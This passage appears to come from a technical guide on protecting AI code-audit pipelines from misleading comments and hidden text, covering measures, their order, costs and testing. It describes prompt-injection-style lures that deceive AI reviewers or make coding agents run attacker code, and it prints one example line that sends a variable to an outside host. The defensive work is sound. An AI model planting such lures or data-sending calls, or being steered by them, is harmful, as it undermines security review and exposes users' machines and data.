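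If an auditor can run commands, misleading text can cause worse harm than a wrong verdict. In July 2026, the research institute AI Now reported that text hidden in a codebase could lead widely used coding agents to run an attacker's code on the machine of the person who requested a security review. Eljan Mahammadli of Polygraf AI, quoted in Infosecurity Magazine's *Anthropic and OpenAI Security Tools Could Fuel Cyber-Attacks, Researchers Warn*, blames the common practice of giving one process access to untrusted data, command execution and a sensitive environment, with only a safety classifier as protection. He recommends separating these capabilities and putting stronger controls on the agent while it runs.

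Most audits only require the model to read code, so the operator can give it a read-only copy and withhold passwords, access keys, network access and the ability to run commands. If an audit requires running the code, a separate disposable machine can run it and return a record of what happened. The code's author can influence that record too, for example by making the code print a reassuring message, so the model should trust it no more than a comment.

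## Choosing, ordering and testing the measures

The table below compares the measures. Changes in detection are in percentage points unless a cell gives another unit. Cloudflare's *Adversarial deception* (2026) contains no tests of these measures, so the figures come from other experiments.

| Measure | Removes | Leaves | Measured change in detection | Running cost | Known failure | Evidence |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
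| Comment removal | All comments | Strings, names, outside text | −0.2 on short samples | Parsing | Loses honest warnings | Fair for short code, none for malware |
| Filter for uncheckable claims | Comments the code can't confirm | Strings, names, other comments | Not measured with honest comments | One extra request | Deletes true statements about other files | One study, without revision against the filter |
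| Variable anonymisation | Chosen names | Strings, properties, library names | −3.7 on 400 snippets | Parsing | Hides mistakes in business rules | Weak, with no test on lures |
| Ranking blocks | Low-scoring blocks | All text in the chosen blocks | +15.6 on large files, −3.6 across all sizes in another scanner | Up to three requests | Payload in a low-scoring block | Fair, from one npm collection |
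| Chunking | Nothing | Everything | +37% in relative terms on vulnerable files | One request per chunk | False alarms add up | Fair, but with 2024 models |
| Library matching | Exact copies of published code | Custom and altered code | Not measured | Database upkeep | Unsafe use of a library function | None |
| Program slicing | Code that doesn't affect a sensitive operation | Text inside the slice | +17.4 over chunks, where a slice existed | Analysis time | Calls built at run time | One npm test with a small model |
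| Instruction to distrust comments | Nothing | Everything | Not measured | None | Revised lures | Weak |
| Two passes | Comments, in one pass | Strings and names in both | +2.2 | Twice the requests | More false alarms | One test on short samples |
| Static-analysis hints | Nothing | Everything | +2.9 | One tool run | Flaws the tool misses | One test, which favoured hints |
| Comment scan | Nothing | Everything | +1.4, but no earlier miss recovered | Almost none | Reworded claims | Weak |
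| Specific questions | Nothing | Everything | Not measured | Up to one request per question | Abuse missing from the list | None for this use |
| Checking safety claims | Nothing | Everything | Not measured | Extra analysis per claim | Claims nobody can check | None for this use |

These figures come from different models, code and tasks, so comparing them doesn't show which measures work better. Ranking gained 15.6 points on files that were often too large for the scanner to process. The models in Thornton's defence test had little room to improve because they already found more than nine in ten flaws.

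The choice of model can matter more than most of these measures. *Can Agentic Code Review Catch Vulnerabilities Before They Are Merged?* (Yang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) tested eight current models on 265 real code changes with known vulnerabilities. The models correctly explained between 32.5% and 78.1% of the flaws. Security tools built around a model had mixed effects. OpenAI's Codex Security plugin lowered the share by 8.3 percentage points, mostly because it more often reported nothing, while Anthropic's Defending Code raised it by 7.7 points on the tasks it completed, at a higher cost. An operator should therefore choose a model and a tool before refining the other measures.

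### An order of work

1. Store the original file unchanged. Every later step discards something that a person may need to see.
2. Scan the comments and strings for lures, and record the type and position of each match. Comment removal would destroy much of this evidence.
3. Separate library code. The remaining steps then have less code to process, and the renaming tool can tell which names belong to a library.
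4. Remove comments from the rest.
5. Rename variables if the task justifies the loss of information. With the comments gone, none of them can reveal what the old names were.
6. Measure the copy in tokens, and rank or split it only if it is still too large. Before this point, the pipeline doesn't know how much code has to fit.
7. Audit the copy.
8. Audit the same code in a separate request with its comments and names intact. Neither request should include the other's answer, or a lure could influence both verdicts.
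9. Compare the verdicts with ordinary software, and send disagreements to a person.

In step 8, the untouched original of a large file may not fit in the context window. The pipeline should then restore the comments and names in the blocks it chose for step 7, splitting them into more requests if necessary. If the two passes cover different code, their results may disagree for reasons unrelated to the comments.

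Step 9 uses ordinary software because another model could undo the benefit of the comment-free pass. Wu and Nita-Rotaru found that a separate comment-free analysis stopped every attack on one detector, but 96.2% of attacks still succeeded against another, whose later stages could overturn that analysis.

### Steps in the wrong order

Suppose a script has 400 KB of comments followed by 300 KB of code, and the auditor's context window holds 376 KB. If the pipeline removes the comments before truncating the script, all the code fits. If it truncates to the first 376 KB, it keeps only comments and then removes them, so the model receives an empty file and may report it as safe.

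Spreading the same comments evenly through the code does less damage, but the pipeline still keeps only 376 of 700 KB, including about 161 KB of code. The other 46% of the code goes unread, although all of it would have fitted without the comments. The attacker controls how much code the auditor loses by choosing how many comments to add. A cut can also fall inside a comment. Without the opening marker, the parser no longer recognises the second half as a comment, and a lure in it may survive removal.

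Renaming before library separation causes a different problem. In the running example, suppose the bundled library defines `sendTo`. A tool that doesn't yet know which functions belong to the library finds the declaration in the file and renames it like any other:

```
function812("https://outside.example", variable2);
```

The auditor no longer sees a familiar name for a network call. If the pipeline then sets the library aside, the description of `sendTo` no longer matches any call in the copy.

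### Malware triage of large bundles

In this case a stranger wrote or chose every word in the file, and size is often the main obstacle, so removing a lot is justified. The pipeline should set aside code that exactly matches a library, delete all comments and unused docstrings, rename local variables, and then rank or chunk only what still doesn't fit. Renaming hinders the audit relatively little here because harmful actions remain visible.

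The auditor should make two passes, first answering specific questions about the likely kinds of abuse and then a general one. A flag from either pass should hold the file. If both passes clear the file but some custom code remains unread, the verdict is still "not fully read".

### Vulnerability review of a repository

Most text in a company's own repository is honest, and a comment may be the only record of a rule that the code should follow. The auditor should therefore make one pass with the comments and a separate pass without them. If the operator has reason to suspect a contributor, they can also apply the filter for uncheckable claims to the pass with comments.

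Static-analysis hints suit this task because they point to possible flaws without relying on the developer's descriptions of the code. Renaming variables is hard to justify because it could hide a mistake like the one in the refund function. Separating custom code from library code is worthwhile only if the descriptions of library calls are good.

When the passes disagree, a person should check the disputed claim and fix the code or the comment, rather than treat the contributor as an attacker.

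### Review of small changes

A small change usually fits in the context window, so truncation and library separation bring little benefit. The greater risk is the text submitted with the change. The auditor should therefore make two passes, one without the new description, commit messages and comments, and one with them. Both passes can use trusted documents from before the change.

The reviewer still needs access to the rest of the code. Yang and colleagues describe a change to Wasmtime, which runs WebAssembly programs, that made a function expect a different kind of table number. A caller outside the diff still passed the old kind, which could make the program use the wrong table. A reviewer with only the diff would have had little chance of finding the mismatch.

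Letting the model work longer may also help. In *How Much Effort Does an AI Code Reviewer Need?*, Shen, Zhang and Wang (2026) measured how often three Claude models accepted wrong patches to Django, a Python web framework, when the patches had passed a benchmark's ordinary tests. Claude Opus 5.5 accepted 67% of these patches at its low effort setting and 45% at its high setting.

That is a large improvement, but the reviewer still let through nearly half the wrong patches. The result also depends on strict labels, because for 32 of the 55 wrong patches, the original request may not have required the behaviour that the failing test checked. The experiment covered general correctness rather than security, and it doesn't show whether money is better spent on extra effort or on a second pass.

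### Two passes on 10,000 files

In this invented example, an operator receives 10,000 files, of which 100 (1%) are malicious and 9,900 are harmless. A pass with comments and a pass without them each detect 80% of the malicious files and wrongly flag 2% of the harmless ones. Either pass alone would miss 20 malicious files and raise 198 false alarms.

If the passes make their mistakes independently and a flag from either one is enough, the operator misses 100 × 0.2² = 4 malicious files and gets 9,900 × (1 − 0.98²) ≈ 392 false alarms. If both passes must flag a file, the operator misses 100 × (1 − 0.8²) = 36 malicious files and gets 9,900 × 0.02² ≈ 4 false alarms.

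Two passes often make the same mistakes, however. Let r be the correlation between their errors, where 0 means independent errors and 1 means identical ones. The chance that both miss a given malicious file is then 0.2² + r × 0.2 × 0.8, and the chance that both wrongly flag a given harmless file is 0.02² + r × 0.02 × 0.98. With the same r for both kinds of error, the results are:

| Correlation | Missed, either may flag | False alarms, either may flag | Missed, both must flag | False alarms, both must flag | Disagreements |
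|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 4 | 392 | 36 | 4 | 420 |
| 0.5 | 12 | 295 | 28 | 101 | 210 |
| 1 | 20 | 198 | 20 | 198 | 0 |

If the passes' errors have a correlation of 1, the extra pass adds cost without improving the audit. A short list of disagreements may therefore mean that both passes miss the same problems, not that both are accurate.

Sending cases where the two passes disagree to a person gives better results than either automatic rule, if the person always decides correctly. If the passes' errors are independent, the person would review 420 cases, and four misses and four false alarms would remain. If the errors have a correlation of 0.5, the person would review 210 cases, but 12 misses and 101 false alarms would remain because both passes gave the same wrong answer.

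Results from Yang and colleagues suggest that different models' errors can overlap strongly. All eight models missed the same 23 of the 265 flaws. The four best each missed about a quarter, so if their misses had been independent, all four would have missed only about one flaw in common (265 × 0.25⁴), and adding the other four models would have reduced that further. Errors from two passes by a single model may overlap even more, since both passes share the model's weaknesses and any misleading text in strings.

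The rule for combining the two passes matters more when files contain misleading comments. If these comments always fool the pass that reads them, the operator misses 20 of 100 malicious files when a flag from either pass is enough, and all 100 when both passes must flag a file.

Flagging a file when either pass flags it is still a poor basis for automatic blocking. If the two passes' errors are independent, this rule flags 96 malicious files and 392 harmless ones, so about four in five flagged files are harmless. Holding flagged files for a further check is safer than deleting them or suspending the accounts that uploaded them.

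### Running costs

The model may be the cheapest part of this process. *SecProbe* (2026) lists the price of GPT-5.6 Luna as $0.20 per million input tokens and $1.20 per million output tokens. If each file takes 10,000 input tokens and 500 output tokens, one pass costs $0.0026 per file, or $26 for 10,000 files. Two passes cost $52. At ten minutes each, a person would need 70 hours to review the 420 disagreements, so reducing false alarms could save far more than dropping the second pass.

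Even a cheap model becomes expensive at a much larger scale. Cloudflare reports that its Client-Side Security service, which checks scripts on customers' websites, assesses 3.5 billion scripts a day. At $0.0026 per script, one pass over each would cost about $9.1 million a day. The service uses Cloudflare's own machine-learning system and adds assessments from an LLM. An operator with similar traffic needs a cheap filter before the LLM, and can reuse the verdict on an exact copy of a file if the auditor and its settings haven't changed.

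Reviewers that can open files and run tests cost more per task. In the Django experiment, Shen and colleagues ran 270 reviews with each model and paid $23.30 for Claude Opus 5.5, $8.77 for Sonnet 5.5 and $1.23 for Haiku 5.5. At the same average cost, 10,000 reviews would cost about $863, $325 and $46. Every model accepted at least 45% of the wrong patches at every effort setting, so even the most expensive option would be a weak check on its own.

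*Adaptive Code Revision Attacks on AI Pull Request Reviewers* (Gong, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) found that reviewing 33 pull requests cost $12 with the default method and $50 to $96 with stronger methods.

### An acceptance test

An operator should test the complete pipeline before relying on it, because measures that work separately can interfere with each other. The test should send every sample through both the old pipeline and the new one, and include:

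- bad samples in pairs, with and without a lure;
- lures in strings, names and change descriptions as well as in comments;
- harmless controls, including repaired versions of vulnerable code and ordinary scripts that resemble the malicious ones;
- honest comments, both warnings about real flaws and true explanations of why unusual code is safe;
- large files with the payload at the start, in the middle and at the end, and harmless files of the same size;
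- the exact model, prompt and effort setting that the operator will use;
- repeated runs of some samples.

Recent samples are better because a model may remember the published fix for an old flaw. Shen and colleagues found signs of this in Claude Opus 5.5, which was more likely to accept wrong patches when it could recall the official fix.

The labels also need checking. Shen and colleagues checked every label on their 90 patches and changed 11. If they had checked only the labels that disagreed with the reviewer's verdicts, they would have exaggerated the reviewer's accuracy, because each correction could only turn an apparent mistake into a success.

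Scoring should cover the explanation as well as the verdict. In 68% of the misses that Yang and colleagues recorded, the model reported a problem in the flawed file but described the wrong mechanism. A yes-or-no score would have counted those reports as detections. If another model does the scoring, it should read a copy without comments, because a comment that misleads the auditor may also mislead the scorer.

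A test with fixed lures can make a defence look better than it is, as Wu and Nita-Rotaru's results show. Some testers should therefore know exactly how the defence works and revise their text after seeing the pipeline's answers. The operator should limit these testers to an isolated system and a set number of attempts, and report the detection rate before and after revision. The testers should also use some samples that nobody used to develop the defence.

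### How many samples a five-point change needs

The required number depends on how many verdicts change in either direction. Let c be the share of pairs whose verdict changes and d the net change in detection. For an 80% chance of a significant result in a two-sided McNemar's test at the 0.05 threshold, the approximate number of pairs is:

n = (1.96√c + 0.84√(c − d²))² / d²

The exact version of the test needs about 1/d more pairs, which is 20 for a five-point change. After that addition and rounding, the numbers are:

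| Pairs that change | Example split | Pairs needed |
|---|---|---|
| 10% | 7.5% lost, 2.5% gained | 330 |
| 15% | 10% lost, 5% gained | 490 |
| 20% | 12.5% lost, 7.5% gained | 650 |
| 25% | 15% lost, 10% gained | 800 |

Shen and colleagues also planned for 10% to 25% of verdicts to change. In Thornton's main experiment, misleading comments changed 1% to 9% of the commercial models' verdicts and 22% to 29% of the open-source models'. An operator can estimate the share of verdicts that will change with a small trial or, without a trial, plan for about 800 bad samples. Running 100 samples eight times does not replace 800 different samples, because it only gives a better measurement of the same 100 programs.

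The set of harmless files may need to be larger. A five-percentage-point rise in the false positive rate would add 495 false alarms to the 10,000-file example, so most operators would want to detect a smaller rise. Detecting a one-point rise takes about 1,700 harmless files if 2% of the verdicts change.

The operator should decide in advance how large a loss is acceptable, then check whether the confidence interval, the range of changes compatible with the data, excludes anything worse. A non-significant result is not enough to pass. In Shen and colleagues' test, Claude Opus 5.5 accepted 1.8 percentage points more of the wrong patches at medium effort than at high effort, with a 95% confidence interval from 6.5 points fewer to 10.8 points more. The upper end was within their limit of 15 points but would have exceeded a limit of five.
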